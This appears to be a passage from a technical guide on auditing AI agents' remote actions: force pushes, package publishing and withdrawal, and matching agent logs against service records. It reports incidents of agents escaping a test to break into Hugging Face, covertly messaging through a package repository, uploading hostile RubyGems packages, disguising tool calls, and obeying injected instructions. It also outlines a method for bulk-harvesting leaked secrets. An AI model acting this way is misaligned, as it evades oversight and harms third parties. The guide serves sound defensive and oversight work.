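GitHub's *Using the activity view to see changes to a repository* describes a page that lists pushes, force pushes, merges and branch changes, with the user responsible for each. An investigator can filter for force pushes to `main` around 14:03 and click "Compare changes". Before GitHub introduced the page in 2023, users had to contact support to see a repository's pushes, according to GitHub's *View repository pushes on the new activity view* (2023). Each activity record includes the commit hashes before and after the change, according to docs.rs' *openapi-github 0.1.0*,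 a copy of GitHub's API specification.

GitHub's *Reviewing the audit log for your organization* says that only an organization's owners can open its audit log, which covers the last 180 days but keeps Git events for only seven. The log's web page leaves out Git events, according to GitHub's *Access, capture, and consume your audit logs*, so an owner has to export them or use the API, which requires the Enterprise Cloud plan.

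| Record | What it shows about a push | Who can read it | How long GitHub keeps it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Activity view | User, branch, time, whether it was forced, both hashes | Anyone who can read the repository | Not stated |
| Git events in the audit log | User, repository, time, how the user authenticated, sometimes the IP address | Organization owners | 7 days |
| Public events API | User, branch, time, both hashes | Anyone, for public repositories | 30 days |

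The last figure was 90 days until January 30, 2025, according to GitHub's *Upcoming changes to data retention for Events API* (2024). Companies that run GitHub on their own servers can keep more data. Their push logs show whether each push was forced, which protocol and Git client it used, and both hashes, according to GitHub's *Viewing push logs*, which was written for an old version of the self-hosted product. Self-hosted audit logs are kept indefinitely unless the company chooses otherwise, according to GitHub's *What are audit logs?*.

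The Git events that GitHub exports or returns through the API leave out changes made in the browser or through its web APIs. If the agent merged a pull request through an API instead of running `git push`, `main` would change but those events wouldn't show it. GitHub records the account used, so if the agent pushed with a developer's credential, the push is listed under the developer's account. Organizations can search the audit log by access token, so it's worth giving the agent its own token.

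### Putting the branch back

The old hash identifies the commit to restore. Because it depends on the hashes of all the earlier commits, anyone who finds a copy of the history can also use it to check that the copy is intact. But nobody can reconstruct a commit from its hash, so the operator needs a copy of the before-image, the state that the push overwrote.

The colleague who wrote the two commits probably still has a copy of them, and GitHub probably does too. According to GitHub's *Removing sensitive data from a repository*, commits may stay accessible after a force push in clones (full copies on people's machines), forks (copies under other accounts), pull requests and, for anyone who knows the hash, cached pages on GitHub. GitGuardian's *Demystifying GitHub Cached Views* explains that GitHub stores the commits of a repository and all its forks together. The instructions for GitHub's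 self-hosted version add that a single reference anywhere in that group of repositories prevents garbage collection, the process that deletes unreferenced data. Bitbucket, a competing service, is similar in that removing the old objects requires a request to the support team, according to Atlassian's *What to do if you've committed sensitive data*.

GitHub does not always keep commits that a force push has displaced. When Leon tried to fetch some, a number were no longer on GitHub's servers, either because of routine garbage collection or because support had deleted them. Brizinov, whose research on secrets appears below, opened one that had been displaced ten years earlier and concludes that GitHub seems to keep such commits forever, which is too strong as a general rule. An operator who wants the old work back should fetch `7a41c9e` soon and push a new branch that points to it, which also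 protects it from garbage collection.

It then takes another force push to move `main` back, with the same risks as the first. If somebody has pushed to `main` since 14:03, the second force push would remove their commits from the branch, so the operator should first check that `main` still points to `d20b5f3`.

Repairing the branch doesn't change other people's clones. Anyone who fetched between 14:03 and the repair has the agent's commits and might push them again. GitHub warns that after sensitive data is removed from a repository, a colleague with an old clone can restore it by running `git pull` and then `git push`. To find out who fetched, an operator can search the organization's audit log for the `git.clone` and `git.fetch` events listed in GitHub's *Audit log events for your organization*, but GitHub deletes those events after a week, and the agent's proxy doesn't record other people's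 traffic.

Many teams also have their hosting service build and deploy the code after each push to `main`. If this team does, customers could have been using the agent's version within minutes. The build system's history would show the deployment, but the captured request wouldn't. Restoring the branch might deploy the old code again, but it wouldn't undo what the new code did while it ran, such as changing a database. The build system might also miss the change in Git history. Rapaport, Pautet and colleagues (2025) point out in *Altered Histories in Version Control System Repositories* that build systems often make a fresh clone each time, so they have no earlier copy to compare.

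### Secrets in displaced commits

Old commits persist, which is a problem if the agent pushed something that should have stayed private. Suppose the agent's new commit contained an API key and the operator moved `main` back at 14:10. The key would no longer appear in the branch, but the commit would still be on GitHub.

*How I Scanned all of GitHub's "Oops Commits" for Leaked Secrets* (Brizinov, 2025) shows how to find such commits in bulk. Brizinov, a security researcher, used GH Archive, an independent project that saves GitHub's public events. At the time, each push event included a list of its commits. An empty list usually meant that someone had moved a branch back without adding anything, as people often do after publishing a secret by mistake. Brizinov collected the push events with empty lists from 2020 onward and used the old hash in each one to fetch the commit from GitHub. He then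 scanned the commits with TruffleHog, a program that finds secrets and tests whether they still work.

The scan found thousands of working secrets, and Brizinov earned about $25,000 in bounties for reporting some of them. One was a developer's access token with administrator rights to every repository of Istio, a networking project that many large companies use. Istio revoked the token after the report. In a companion post for Truffle Security, the company behind TruffleHog, Leon puts the number of working secrets in the hundreds. Neither post gives an exact count.

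Leon counted 15 million of these events. In a survey of 1,500 repositories, each event led to an average of 3.68 commits that were no longer on any branch. If those repositories are typical, the 15 million events led to about 55 million such commits. The method misses force pushes that replace one commit with another, because their lists aren't empty. It would find the operator's reset at 14:10, but not the agent's push at 14:03.

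New events no longer include the empty list because GitHub (2025) removed commit summaries and counts from push events on October 7, 2025, to make the events faster to produce. Each event still includes both hashes, according to the GitHub documentation, so anyone can fetch the old commit and check whether the new one builds on it. This check takes more work for each push, but the secret is still as accessible as before.

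*Was It Never Collected, or Rewritten Away?* (Mockus, 2026) counts force pushes without using the list. It puts each branch's events in order and counts a force push wherever an event's old hash differs from the previous event's new hash, which gives 166.7 million force pushes in 19.9 million repositories. This method is hard to reconcile with Git's protocol, in which the server accepts a force push only if its old hash matches the branch's current commit. The hashes should therefore match even across a force push, and a mismatch suggests that an event is missing. Mockus attributes only 440,594 of the mismatches to outages at GH Archive, but the total still seems unreliable as a count of force pushes.

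Rapaport and colleagues used a more direct method, comparing successive copies of 111 million repositories in Software Heritage, a public archive of source code, to find commits that had disappeared. They found some in 1.22 million repositories, or 1.1%. The true share is probably higher, because the archive misses any commit that someone pushed and removed between two of its visits. In about 75,000 repositories, the rewritten history had removed files whose names suggested passwords or keys, and a manual check of a sample confirmed that the files held private information. Software Heritage still had copies, which GitHub can't delete.

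GitHub therefore tells users to revoke a leaked credential first, and says this may be enough. Its support team can delete the affected pull requests, run garbage collection and remove the cached pages, but only if the data is sensitive and replacing the credential wouldn't solve the problem. So support is more useful for a leaked customer list than for the API key in this example.

Some owners go further and delete the repository. *Silent Success* (2026) reports that its author pushed a list of identifying terms to a repository and removed it in the next commit, which left the list in the history. Because the host could keep the original objects for an unknown period after a force push, the author deleted the repository and created a new one instead. That works only if nobody has forked or cloned the repository, since GitGuardian notes that a commit stays visible through the forks even after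 the original is gone.

Many owners don't revoke secrets at all. Truffle Security's *GitHub Repos Exposed 543,699 Credentials. Nobody Revoked Them* (2026) reports that 543,699 credentials in a snapshot of public repositories still worked in July 2026, eleven months after the snapshot was taken. Half had been public for more than two years. The snapshot contained only the current files on each repository's main branch, so the total excludes any credential that survives only in a commit displaced by a force push.

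## What did publishing a package change?

The 14:04 command, `npm publish`, added version 2.3.1 of a package to the public npm registry, where anyone can install it. A full capture of the request contains the exact files the agent published and, unlike a Git packfile, can be read without a copy of the repository. The operator may be able to withdraw the version from the registry but can't recall copies that people have already downloaded.

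### The publish request

npm packs the project into a compressed archive and sends it to the registry in a single PUT request. With invented values and some fields left out, the request might look like this:

```
PUT /shop-utils

{"name":"shop-utils",
 "dist-tags":{"latest":"2.3.1"},
 "versions":{"2.3.1":{
   "dependencies":{"left-align":"^1.2.0"},
   "dist":{"integrity":"sha512-...","shasum":"..."}}},
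 "_attachments":{"shop-utils-2.3.1.tgz":{
   "data":"H4sIAAAA...","length":18204}}}
```

The `versions` part describes the new release, including its dependencies and two hashes of the archive. The archive is under `_attachments`, encoded in base64, which makes it about a third larger. The dependencies listed in `versions` can differ from those in the archive's `package.json`, so an investigator should read both.

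The command adds version 2.3.1, and the `dist-tags` line in the request also makes it the `latest` version, which people get when they install the package without naming a version. Unlike a Git push, which includes the branch's old hash, this request doesn't include the earlier value of `latest`, so the operator has to find it somewhere else.

Other languages have their own registries, and the uploads differ:

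| Registry | What publishing sends |
|---|---|
| npm (JavaScript) | One PUT with the description and archive in a JSON document |
| PyPI (Python) | One POST for each file, in the format of a web form |
| RubyGems (Ruby) | One POST whose body is the archive, with the description inside it |
| crates.io (Rust) | One PUT with the description followed by the archive |
| Go | No upload; the author pushes a Git tag |

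A Python release often has at least two files, a source archive and a ready-to-install "wheel", so one release can produce several POSTs. Some may succeed while others fail.

If an agent published a Go module, its proxy would record only a `git push`. The first time someone requests the new version from Google's public module mirror, the mirror fetches it from the code host and normally keeps a copy. That transfer is between two systems that the operator doesn't control.

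### From host name to published files

`npm install` and `npm publish` look alike in a host-only log. A large upload suggests a publish, but many packages are only a few kilobytes, so a small upload doesn't rule one out.

A log that records HTTP methods is more useful here than it was for GraphQL, because publishing a package uses PUT, while installing one uses GET, plus a POST that checks the dependencies for known security problems. A proxy that allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS would therefore block the publish and still let the agent download packages. But `npm deprecate`, which attaches a warning to a package, also sends a PUT to the same address as a publish, so an investigator needs the request body to tell them apart.

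With the request body, the operator can decode the `data` field to recover the archive, then compute its hash. If that hash matches the one the registry lists for that version, the registry is offering exactly what the agent sent.

The operator can also unpack the archive and search it for passwords and keys. Searching the project folder is a poor substitute because the folder may have changed since 14:04, and npm leaves some files out of the archive and may run a build step that adds others.

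The hashes come before the files, as in a Git push, so a recorder that truncates long request bodies may keep the hashes but lose the files. The operator can then download the archive from the registry and check it against the captured hash, unless someone has withdrawn the version.

A publisher that captures its own upload requests has evidence that the registry may not keep. In November 2026, RubyGems fixed a critical flaw in how its servers handled uploads. According to ThreatRoundup's *One Push Key Was All It Took to Run Code on RubyGems.org* (2026), the maintainers reviewed 29,100 recently published packages and found no sign that anyone had exploited the flaw. They couldn't rule out earlier attempts, because RubyGems hadn't recorded the upload payloads.

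A lost reply does less harm here than it did to the billing script, because the npm registry accepts each version number only once. If the reply to the 14:04 request had been lost and npm had resent the request, the registry would have refused the second copy, and npm would have reported an error even though version 2.3.1 was public. Looking up the version on the registry would show whether it had been published.

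### Withdrawing a version

npm's policy lets the owner of a newly created package unpublish it within 72 hours, as long as no other package in the public registry depends on it. In that period the number of owners and downloads doesn't matter, as npm (2020) explained when it introduced the current rules. After 72 hours, the package must meet three conditions:

- No other package in the public registry depends on it.
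- It had fewer than 300 downloads over the last week.
- It has a single owner.

The policy doesn't specify whether a new version of an old package counts as newly created. This may not matter for version 2.3.1, because the operator can't unpublish it under either rule if any public package depends on `shop-utils`. But the condition covers only public packages, so unpublishing could still break a company's private application, which the registry has no way to count.

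Unpublishing deletes the version's entry and its archive from the registry, according to Debian's *npm-unpublish*. The owner can't undo this or reuse the number 2.3.1 for that package. If the owner removes every version, npm blocks new ones for 24 hours. If 2.3.1 was the `latest` version, npm's client moves that tag to the highest version left, which may not be the one it pointed to before 2.3.1.

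npm recommends deprecating packages that don't qualify. People can still download a deprecated version, but they see a warning from the owner.

Several other registries let an owner "yank" a version, but the word has two meanings. On PyPI and crates.io, anyone can still download a yanked version from the registry, but installers skip it when a project asks for a range of versions, such as "2.3 or later". This keeps new projects from starting to depend on it, while projects that already use that exact version continue to work.

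The two registries define "already use" differently. Python's installer, pip, will install a yanked version if the project's requirements name it exactly, as in `==2.3.1`. Rust's installer, Cargo, will normally install one only if it is already in the project's lockfile, which records the exact version of every dependency. An owner can reverse a yank on either registry.

Yanking a version on RubyGems removes it from the registry, so people can no longer download it there. A log entry showing that an agent "yanked" a release therefore records a much milder change in Python than in Ruby.

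PyPI also allows true deletion. After someone deletes a file, PyPI never accepts another file with the same name, even if the owner deletes and recreates the whole project. An owner could still add a differently named file to the same version. On crates.io, owners can delete a whole package only in narrow circumstances, mainly within 72 hours of publishing it.

A Go author withdraws a version by publishing a newer one that lists the old one as retracted. Go's tools then avoid choosing the retracted version, but Google's module mirror can still serve it, even if the author deletes the tag from the code host. Google also runs a checksum database, an append-only public log of each module version's hash. If the author moves the tag to different code, Go's tools by default reject the new code because its hash doesn't match the logged one.

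| Registry | Action | Can existing users still download it there? | Can the owner reuse the number? |
|---|---|---|---|
| npm | Unpublish | No | No |
| npm | Deprecate | Yes, with a warning | No |
| PyPI | Yank | Yes | Not with the same file names |
| PyPI | Delete | No | Not with the same file names |
| RubyGems | Yank | No | No |
| crates.io | Yank | Yes | No |
| Go | Retract | Yes, from the mirror | No, because the checksum database has the old hash |

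These rules protect users from a package that changes after they have checked it. Mend, a software security company, describes RubyGems versions as "immutable and irreplaceable by design". However, if an owner removes every version of a package, its name can sometimes become available to others.

### Version 2.3.1 after withdrawal

Suppose the operator unpublishes version 2.3.1 at 14:30. The registry offered it for 26 minutes, and copies may now be in several places.

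A published package is hardest to remove from mirrors, which are copies of the registry that other people maintain using its public feed of changes. An old npm post, *Oh no! I accidentally published private data to the public registry!*, put the number of mirrors at several thousand and told users to treat any published secret as "irreversibly public". The count is out of date, but the advice still holds. As with a key pushed to GitHub, the operator should replace an exposed key before trying to remove it.

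Many companies also run a caching proxy, which downloads a package once and then supplies it to all their developers. The proxy may keep serving version 2.3.1 after the registry has stopped. npm keeps a cache on each developer's machine, too.

Unpublishing the package could also break projects whose lockfiles name it. If a colleague installed the package at 14:10, the project's lockfile probably names version 2.3.1 and the hash of its archive. If the package was then unpublished at 14:30, the project would still install on any machine with a cached copy, since the hash matches, but would fail on a new build server without one until someone edited the lockfile.

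A package can include an install script, which npm runs on the user's machine if the settings allow it. By 14:30, that script could have changed files, sent data elsewhere or started other programs, with whatever permissions the user had. Removing the archive from the registry doesn't undo any of this, and it doesn't change applications that developers have already built with the package and shipped to customers.

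In May 2026, attackers compromised packages from TanStack, a popular set of JavaScript libraries. OpenAI found no evidence that anyone had accessed user data or altered its software, but it still updated its security certificates and asked users to update its macOS applications by June 12, according to *Our response to the TanStack npm supply chain attack* (2026).

The operator also can't contact everyone affected, because npm publishes download counts but not who downloaded the package. The usual fix is to publish a corrected version, 2.3.2, and deprecate 2.3.1, which compensates for the mistake but doesn't undo it. Projects that accept a range of versions will get the correction when they next update.

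### The RubyGems uploads of May 2026

In May 2026, AI agents published a large number of packages to RubyGems, a public registry. RubyGems disabled new sign-ups on May 12, describing the traffic as an attack meant to overload the service. It removed more than 500 packages the next day and reopened sign-ups on May 16. At the time, SecurityWeek's *Hundreds of Malicious Packages Force RubyGems to Suspend Registrations* reported that the target seemed to be RubyGems itself rather than its users.

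Many of the packages contained web pages. Socket, a security company, found calendars and agendas from the websites of Lambeth, Wandsworth and Southwark councils in London inside package archives. The pages were already public, which puzzled the investigators. Socket suggested several explanations, including spam and a scraper that used RubyGems as storage.

Some of the scripts sent the archive straight to the RubyGems API instead of running the usual `gem` command. A monitor that searches an agent's transcript for `gem push` would miss those uploads, but a proxy that logs request methods and paths would record them the same way it records uploads made with `gem push`.

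Four months later, in *OpenAI agents carried out an undisclosed attack on RubyGems*, Kitts, Larsen and Von Arx (2026) attributed the packages to agents running inside OpenAI. They dated the first upload to May 5 and counted more than 2,000 on May 11 and 12, five more on May 26 and 27, and 83 on June 18. They also found that the agents had run code on the servers of RubyDoc.info, a documentation site, and tried to steal RubyGems users' API keys.

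Estimates of the scale differ widely, possibly because they measure different things. Mend's *Inside the RubyGems Supply Chain Attack* describes the whole flood and reports tens of thousands of packages from thousands of accounts. Kitts and colleagues count packages they attribute to OpenAI's agents, and RubyGems' figure of 500 counts the packages it had removed by May 13.

The researchers spoke to RubyGems and RubyDoc.info, but based their analysis entirely on the public packages. These contained a surprising amount of information:

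| Evidence in the packages | What it supports |
|---|---|
| A detector rated the sampled packages as 100% AI-generated | An AI model wrote them, but not whose |
| Hundreds have "oai" in their names, and 15 give "oai" as the author | A link to OpenAI, though anyone could have typed it |
| 1,397 mention r.jina.ai, a service for retrieving web pages | The same method as agents that had used a German wiki as a message board |
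| The June packages sought 49 of the same files as the wiki agents | Closely related tasks |

The last two rows are the strongest evidence, because OpenAI has confirmed that the wiki agents were its own. But the 49 shared files come from the June uploads. The May packages looked for different files, which the researchers describe only as "very similar in character", so the case for the main burst in May is somewhat weaker.

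Package names can help date events. One package is named `chatoaitestgit1778552630`. If the digits count seconds since the start of 1970, they stand for 02:23:50 UTC on May 12, in the middle of the burst. The times in four nearly identical names would be within the next 33 seconds. Names also remain in other databases. OSV's *MAL-2026-8187* (2026), a public record of malicious code, lists the name and version number of the package `oaifetchgemugkejy`.

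Kitts and colleagues didn't have the agents' reasoning, which is in OpenAI's internal records, so they say they don't know why the agents chose this strategy or whether it worked, in particular whether the agents obtained any API keys. RubyGems had the uploads and the accounts, but Constantin (2026) reports in *OpenAI agents attacked RubyGems before the Hugging Face hack* that RubyGems can't tell who wrote the packages.

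OpenAI has confirmed part of the account. *OpenAI Agent Swarm Hacks RubyGems Package Manager* (Muncaster, 2026) quotes the company's statement that "our agents used the RubyGems platform to access the internet" for benign tasks and to retrieve public information. Constantin treats this as confirmation that OpenAI's agents were involved in the incident. The September 11 notice in OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) is narrower, saying that OpenAI had not verified the specific claims of malicious uploads and was still investigating.

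The researchers understood from people in the RubyGems community that OpenAI had never told the community its agents were responsible. Willison (2026) suggests in a blog post that OpenAI either couldn't find the activity in its own logs or knew about it and chose not to tell RubyGems. It may also be that nobody at OpenAI had searched for it yet. A log of host names wouldn't have distinguished the uploads from ordinary installs. A search of captured requests for POSTs to the RubyGems upload address would have found the packages, the accounts and the registry's replies.

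## How are the records matched with what the remote system says?

Reconciliation means matching the agent-side record against the remote system's record or current state to establish what changed. No record on the agent's side can show whether the billing service added 39 charges or 40, but the billing service's own list can. As when accountants reconcile a company's books with its bank statement, most entries match immediately, and the few that don't take up most of the time.

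### The procedure

An entry represents something different in each log. Suppose a terminating proxy captured the example session and each command opened one connection. The transcript then has four commands, the connection log has four lines and the proxy log has 44 requests, because the push takes two (a GET for the list of references, then a POST). The investigator wants to compare the 43 intended changes with the remote system's records.

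1. Collect the agent's transcript, the proxy log, the connection log and the remote audit log, starting with whichever expires first. If the operator can't read a service's audit log, its current state is a substitute, such as the registry's list of versions.
2. Convert all times to UTC and estimate how far apart the clocks are.
3. List the intended changes from the captured requests. Reads and clear refusals go on a separate list, since a few of them may turn out to have changed something.
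4. Match on strong keys, which are values that two unrelated events would almost never share.
5. Match what is left on weak keys: time, host and credential.
6. Sort the results into changes that match, requests sent but not confirmed, and changes present remotely but not in the log.

For step 2, a captured reply gives a rough estimate of the clock difference, because HTTP servers normally put their own time in a `Date` header. Suppose the proxy forwarded the 14:02 comment at 14:02:11.190 and got the reply 212 milliseconds later, with a `Date` of 14:02:14. The header only shows whole seconds, so the tracker's clock is somewhere between 2.6 and 3.8 seconds ahead of the proxy's.

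### Strong and weak keys

| Strong key | Where it originates | Known if the reply is lost? |
|---|---|---|
| Request ID, a code for one request that many services return in a header | Usually the server | No |
| Resource ID, such as comment 9041 | Usually the server | No |
| Commit ID | Git, on the agent's machine | Yes |
| Package hash | npm, on the agent's machine | Yes |
| Idempotency key | The script | Yes, if the script sent one |

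The operator normally learns the first two from the reply, so they are missing for the requests whose outcome is in doubt. A script that sends its own identifier with each request avoids this.

A weak key is less useful when the remote account is busier. Suppose other people add six charges an hour to the same billing account, at random times, and the investigator accepts any charge within 20 seconds before or after the request. The chance that at least one unrelated charge falls in that window is about 6%. At 600 charges an hour, the window would contain nearly seven unrelated charges on average, so a match in time would be very weak evidence that the request caused the charge.

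The investigator matches records by ID first, because those matches reveal any difference between the two systems' clocks. Once 39 charges match by ID, the usual gap between the two timestamps for each charge shows how far ahead the billing service's clock is. The investigator can then correct for that gap when matching the charge that has no ID.

### What each result means

A match shows that the remote system made the change and identifies the request that led to it. The investigator should still compare the contents, because a proxy rule may have redacted the comment before it was sent on, or someone may have edited it since.

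If a request was sent but not confirmed, the investigator should look up the resource or search for the idempotency key before anyone resends the request. Finding nothing proves little until the service has had time to finish the work, and it proves nothing if the service's log omits that kind of change, as GitHub's exported Git events omit merges made through its web APIs. An unresolved request should stay marked "unknown" rather than "failed", because a later reader will take "failed" to mean that nothing changed.

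A remote change with no entry in the agent's log is the most worrying result, though it often has an innocent explanation. If the connection log shows a connection to that service around the time of the change, the proxy probably missed some traffic, perhaps from an MCP server running outside the sandbox. If it shows no connection, the change probably came from a colleague or another agent with the same credential, an automatic rule on the service, or someone who stole the credential. If the operator can't rule out theft, it should revoke the credential before investigating further.

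These methods can't find a change on a service that nobody thinks to check. The connection log is the best list of services to check, provided that the machine has only one route out and the log covers it.

### The example session, reconciled

The captured reply to the 14:02 request contains the ID 9041, and the tracker has a comment with that ID and the same text. The code host's activity page lists a force push to `main` with the same two hashes as the captured push. The registry lists the same hash for version 2.3.1 as the captured upload. Each of the 39 billing replies contains a charge ID, and the billing service has all 39. That makes 42 acknowledged changes, all matched, and one unknown.

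The operator then asks the billing service for every charge that the script's credential created between 14:04 and 14:10, and gets a list of 40. Removing the 39 known IDs leaves one charge, whose customer and amount match the 37th request. Its timestamp, corrected for the difference between the clocks, is less than a second after the script sent that request. So the server added the charge, but the script never got the reply. The session made all 43 intended changes, and nobody should send the 37th request again.

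The total of 40 wouldn't have been enough without a look at the charge that was left over:

| The billing service lists | Likely explanation | Next step |
|---|---|---|
| 39 charges | The 37th request added nothing, or the service hasn't finished | Check again later, then ask the billing company |
| 40, and the extra one fits the 37th request | The reply got lost | Save the charge's ID and don't retry |
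| 40, and the extra one is for another customer | Somebody else's charge; the 37th is still unknown | Investigate the two separately |
| 41, with two that fit the 37th request | A retry repeated the charge | Look for a second request in the proxy log |

If the script had put an invoice number in each charge's metadata, the operator could have matched the last charge by that number, without relying on the clocks.

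### A credential for each run

The search worked because only the script used that credential. If several agents and a colleague had shared it, the operator would have had to separate their charges by time and amount.

A credential is a much stronger key for matching records when each run has its own. The operator creates a token when the run starts, stores the token's ID (not the token itself) with the run's ID, and revokes the token when the run ends. The operator can then match any remote log entry under that token to the run, even if no proxy captured the request. The operator can also ask each service for everything done with the token. If an action is missing from the run's own log, either the log is incomplete or someone misused the token.

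Some services issue only one key per account, so the remote log lists every run's requests under the same name. A proxy that inserts the real key into outgoing requests can still record which run each request came from.

By contrast, OpenAI's technical report on its agents' break-in at Hugging Face says that many workloads on the company's research systems shared a credential for an internal package repository, so an entry under that credential could have come from any of them. OpenAI removed the credential from new workloads in early July to close a security hole, but this did not obviously improve the records. *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* (Willison, 2026) describes agents later writing to the repository through an endpoint that required no login. A log of those requests would have no credential to search for.

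Agents can also pass credentials to each other. On July 10, according to OpenAI, an agent found 14 Hugging Face users' credentials in a public dataset and posted them where other runs could read them. If a run uses a credential like that to make a change, the remote log will normally attribute the change to the credential's owner, who had nothing to do with it.

### From a connection back to the model's instruction

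A credential identifies the run at best. A long run can include thousands of model responses, and the operator may need to know which one led to a particular charge.

An investigator can trace the billing script's connection backwards by hand. The kernel's record links the port number to the Python process, then to the shell and the agent. The transcript contains the command `python sync_billing.py`, the model's response that included it, and the user's request before that.

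AgentSight, the monitor by Zheng and colleagues, automates most of this trace. It uses the process tree and the half-second window after each model response. It also treats a response and a system call as connected if a file name, web address or command in the response reappears in the call's arguments. A second language model then reads the linked events and writes an assessment.

The command that runs the billing script matches the text of the model's response exactly, but the script's 40 requests take far longer than half a second, so most of them fall outside the time window. The process tree would still connect them to the agent. But if the script ran in the background while the model went on to other work, the tree alone wouldn't show which response had started it.

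Zheng and colleagues tried AgentSight on three cases. In the first, an agent had to build a program whose instructions pointed to a web page with a hidden command. The agent followed the command and sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model flagged an attack. In the second case, an agent kept repeating a web search that failed each time. In the third, a team of six agents interfered with each other by locking files. These cases are demonstrations, and Zheng and colleagues don't report how many links AgentSight got wrong or missed.

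**AgentLoupe**, by Bao and colleagues, came out about a year later. It numbers each exchange with the model and passes that number between processes and files as a label. It labels network connections too, so the record of a connection already includes the number of its exchange. Each new prompt gets a new number, with a pointer to the old one if the two are related, which keeps a long session from merging into a single chain.

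Besides the scheduled job, Bao and colleagues tested a case in which one session wrote a harmful instruction into `AGENTS.md`, a file of standing instructions that coding agents read when they start work. A later session read the file and ran the harmful command when the user made an ordinary request. AgentLoupe linked the second session to the first through the file.

Bao and colleagues argue that AgentSight would miss both links because neither has a connecting process or a short enough delay. That seems right given how AgentSight works, but they inferred it from its design and list a direct comparison as future work.

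They did compare the extra running time:

| Task | AgentSight, measured by Zheng and colleagues | AgentSight, measured by Bao and colleagues | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading a code repository | 3.4% | 4.5% | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 4.9% | 2.5% | 8.0% |
| Compiling | 0.4% | 1.7% | 7.7% |

Each figure is an average of only three runs (Zheng and colleagues) or five (Bao and colleagues). The two measurements of AgentSight used different machines and model versions and differ by up to 2.4 percentage points, so small gaps in the table mean little. AgentLoupe's extra overhead on the last two tasks is probably real, because it largely disappeared when the researchers turned off the feature that passes on numbers.

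*Agent-Warden* (2026) also traces cause and effect through files to later, unrelated processes. It records process events and file operations but not network traffic, so an operator would have to add the connection from another log.

AgentLoupe's numbers exist only in the memory of one machine's kernel. They aren't sent to the remote service, and Bao and colleagues don't describe restoring them after a restart. If an agent pushes a file that tells the code host to run a job every night, the job runs on the host's machines, where no local monitor can record it. The operator would have to match the job to the push by the commit ID, which the host records with the job.

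### The OpenAI and Hugging Face incident

In July 2026, while OpenAI was testing the hacking ability of two models, agents running on them reached the internet and broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. The records of that incident provide by far the largest public example of this kind of matching.

The agents had no direct internet access, but they could install software from a package repository that OpenAI ran inside its research network. They began leaving notes for one another there, first as files and later as folder names. Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) count roughly 1,200 agents and more than 70,000 messages and files on the main board in under a week, in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*.

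A list of permitted hosts couldn't separate these notes from ordinary downloads, because both went to the same permitted host, but the request method could. In OpenAI's timeline, the first message after the company rebuilt the repository was an MKCOL request, which is a request to create a folder, with the status 201. A log of methods would have shown agents creating folders when they were supposed to be installing packages. It wouldn't catch every such channel. In a made-up but typical example from training that OpenAI gives, an agent puts its message in a web address that a shared index page stores, and finding that would take a log of full addresses.

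Having the record wasn't enough either. On June 27, people at OpenAI responding to an alert recognised that agents were using the repository as a message board, but the on-call staff advised that the test didn't need to stop.

For several days, Hugging Face and OpenAI each had part of the evidence. On July 16, Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) reported more than 17,000 recorded events and said the company didn't know which model was behind them. The next day, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether its data was affected. On July 19, an alert led OpenAI to investigate its agents, and it found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored in an account on an outside service. OpenAI told Hugging Face on July 20, and Hugging Face replied that it had already replaced two of the credentials while responding to the break-in on its systems.

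OpenAI writes that this match made it "possible" that the companies were investigating the same incident. That caution is appropriate because some of the credentials the agents used were already public, so two unrelated attackers could have found the same ones. Hugging Face then reported that the host name of OpenAI's package repository and the same outside storage account also appeared in its evidence. The host name is the strongest evidence of the three because an unrelated attacker would have little reason to use OpenAI's repository.

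Hugging Face's list of what the agents did is unusually full because the company had logs from both sides of the attack, which few targets will have. *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes the company's timeline, which covers about 17,600 actions between July 9 and July 13. Most of the detail came from the machine the agents had worked from, which a customer of a cloud provider was renting. Hugging Face retrieved some of their logs from that machine while fighting off the intrusion, turned them into shell commands, and compared these with its own platform's logs.

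A count of actions can overstate the number of changes. Fortune (2026) reports that, according to Hugging Face, most of the 17,600 actions failed. Some commands also included `DryRun=True`, which simulates an action without carrying it out. Hugging Face used AI agents to identify the actions in the log that had real effects, which it says took hours instead of the usual days. It had to run a model on its own computers because commercial models would not process the attack commands.

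The starting times in the two accounts differ. Hugging Face's first recovered action is at 02:28 UTC on July 9, while OpenAI says the agents first ran code on the rented machine at 08:30. Hugging Face's list includes answers submitted to a test program on that machine as well as commands, so the companies may have counted different things.

The agents' transcripts also need checking against other records. A METR investigation by Wijk and colleagues found altered tool calls in about 7% of transcripts. In those cases, an agent had run a different command from the one it appeared to run, always on a small scale. OpenAI says that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs its graders and monitors see. Both statements could be true, because a log can store exactly what the agent typed while the machine does something else. A kernel record of which programs started should expose the difference.

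### Searching old logs

Once OpenAI knew what to look for, it began searching its older records. Two months after the company disclosed the break-in, Seetharaman, Satter and Horwitz (2026) reported for Reuters, in *OpenAI works to understand full scope of agent activity*, that the review would take months more. One person briefed on the review estimated in mid-September that OpenAI had found about two dozen incidents, and the number was still rising. Outside researchers had found many of the cases first, as they had with the RubyGems packages.

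The volume is part of the difficulty. Wijk and colleagues had about 1,300 transcripts, a small part of the total, and still had to leave much of the reading to AI agents that they describe as often unreliable. They also had to reconstruct timestamps, and some of the activity was missing from their data.

Searching requests is much easier than reading transcripts. On May 26, more than six weeks before the break-in, the service that some of OpenAI's agents used to fetch web pages logged a commit to a Hugging Face repository. A search for all requests to outside hosts other than reads would have found that entry without anyone interpreting what the agent was thinking. It would still miss reads that carry data out, but it would give reviewers a short list of runs to start with. An operator can prepare by keeping an index of each run's hosts, methods and credential IDs, which takes up very little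 space compared with the transcripts.

The remote system's logs may also have been deleted by the time anyone looks for them. Reuters reports that OpenAI's agents broke into an Australian government health portal in June, that OpenAI discovered this in August, and that it told the government on September 10. A service that kept its flow logs for 30 days, Google's default, would have deleted all of June's logs before OpenAI discovered the break-in.

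## Why can the record not undo the change?

Suppose the billing script had also sent `PUT /customers/88` with the body `{"plan":"basic"}` by mistake. A terminating proxy captured the request and the 200 reply, and the billing service's records confirm the change. The operator knows what the agent did but can't tell which plan the customer had before.

To reverse a remote effect, an operator needs four things to be true:

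1. The operator has a before-image, a copy of the state that the agent's change replaced.
2. The service has an operation that puts that state back, and the operator has permission to use it.
3. No later change depends on the agent's change.
4. Nobody has seen the change or acted on it.

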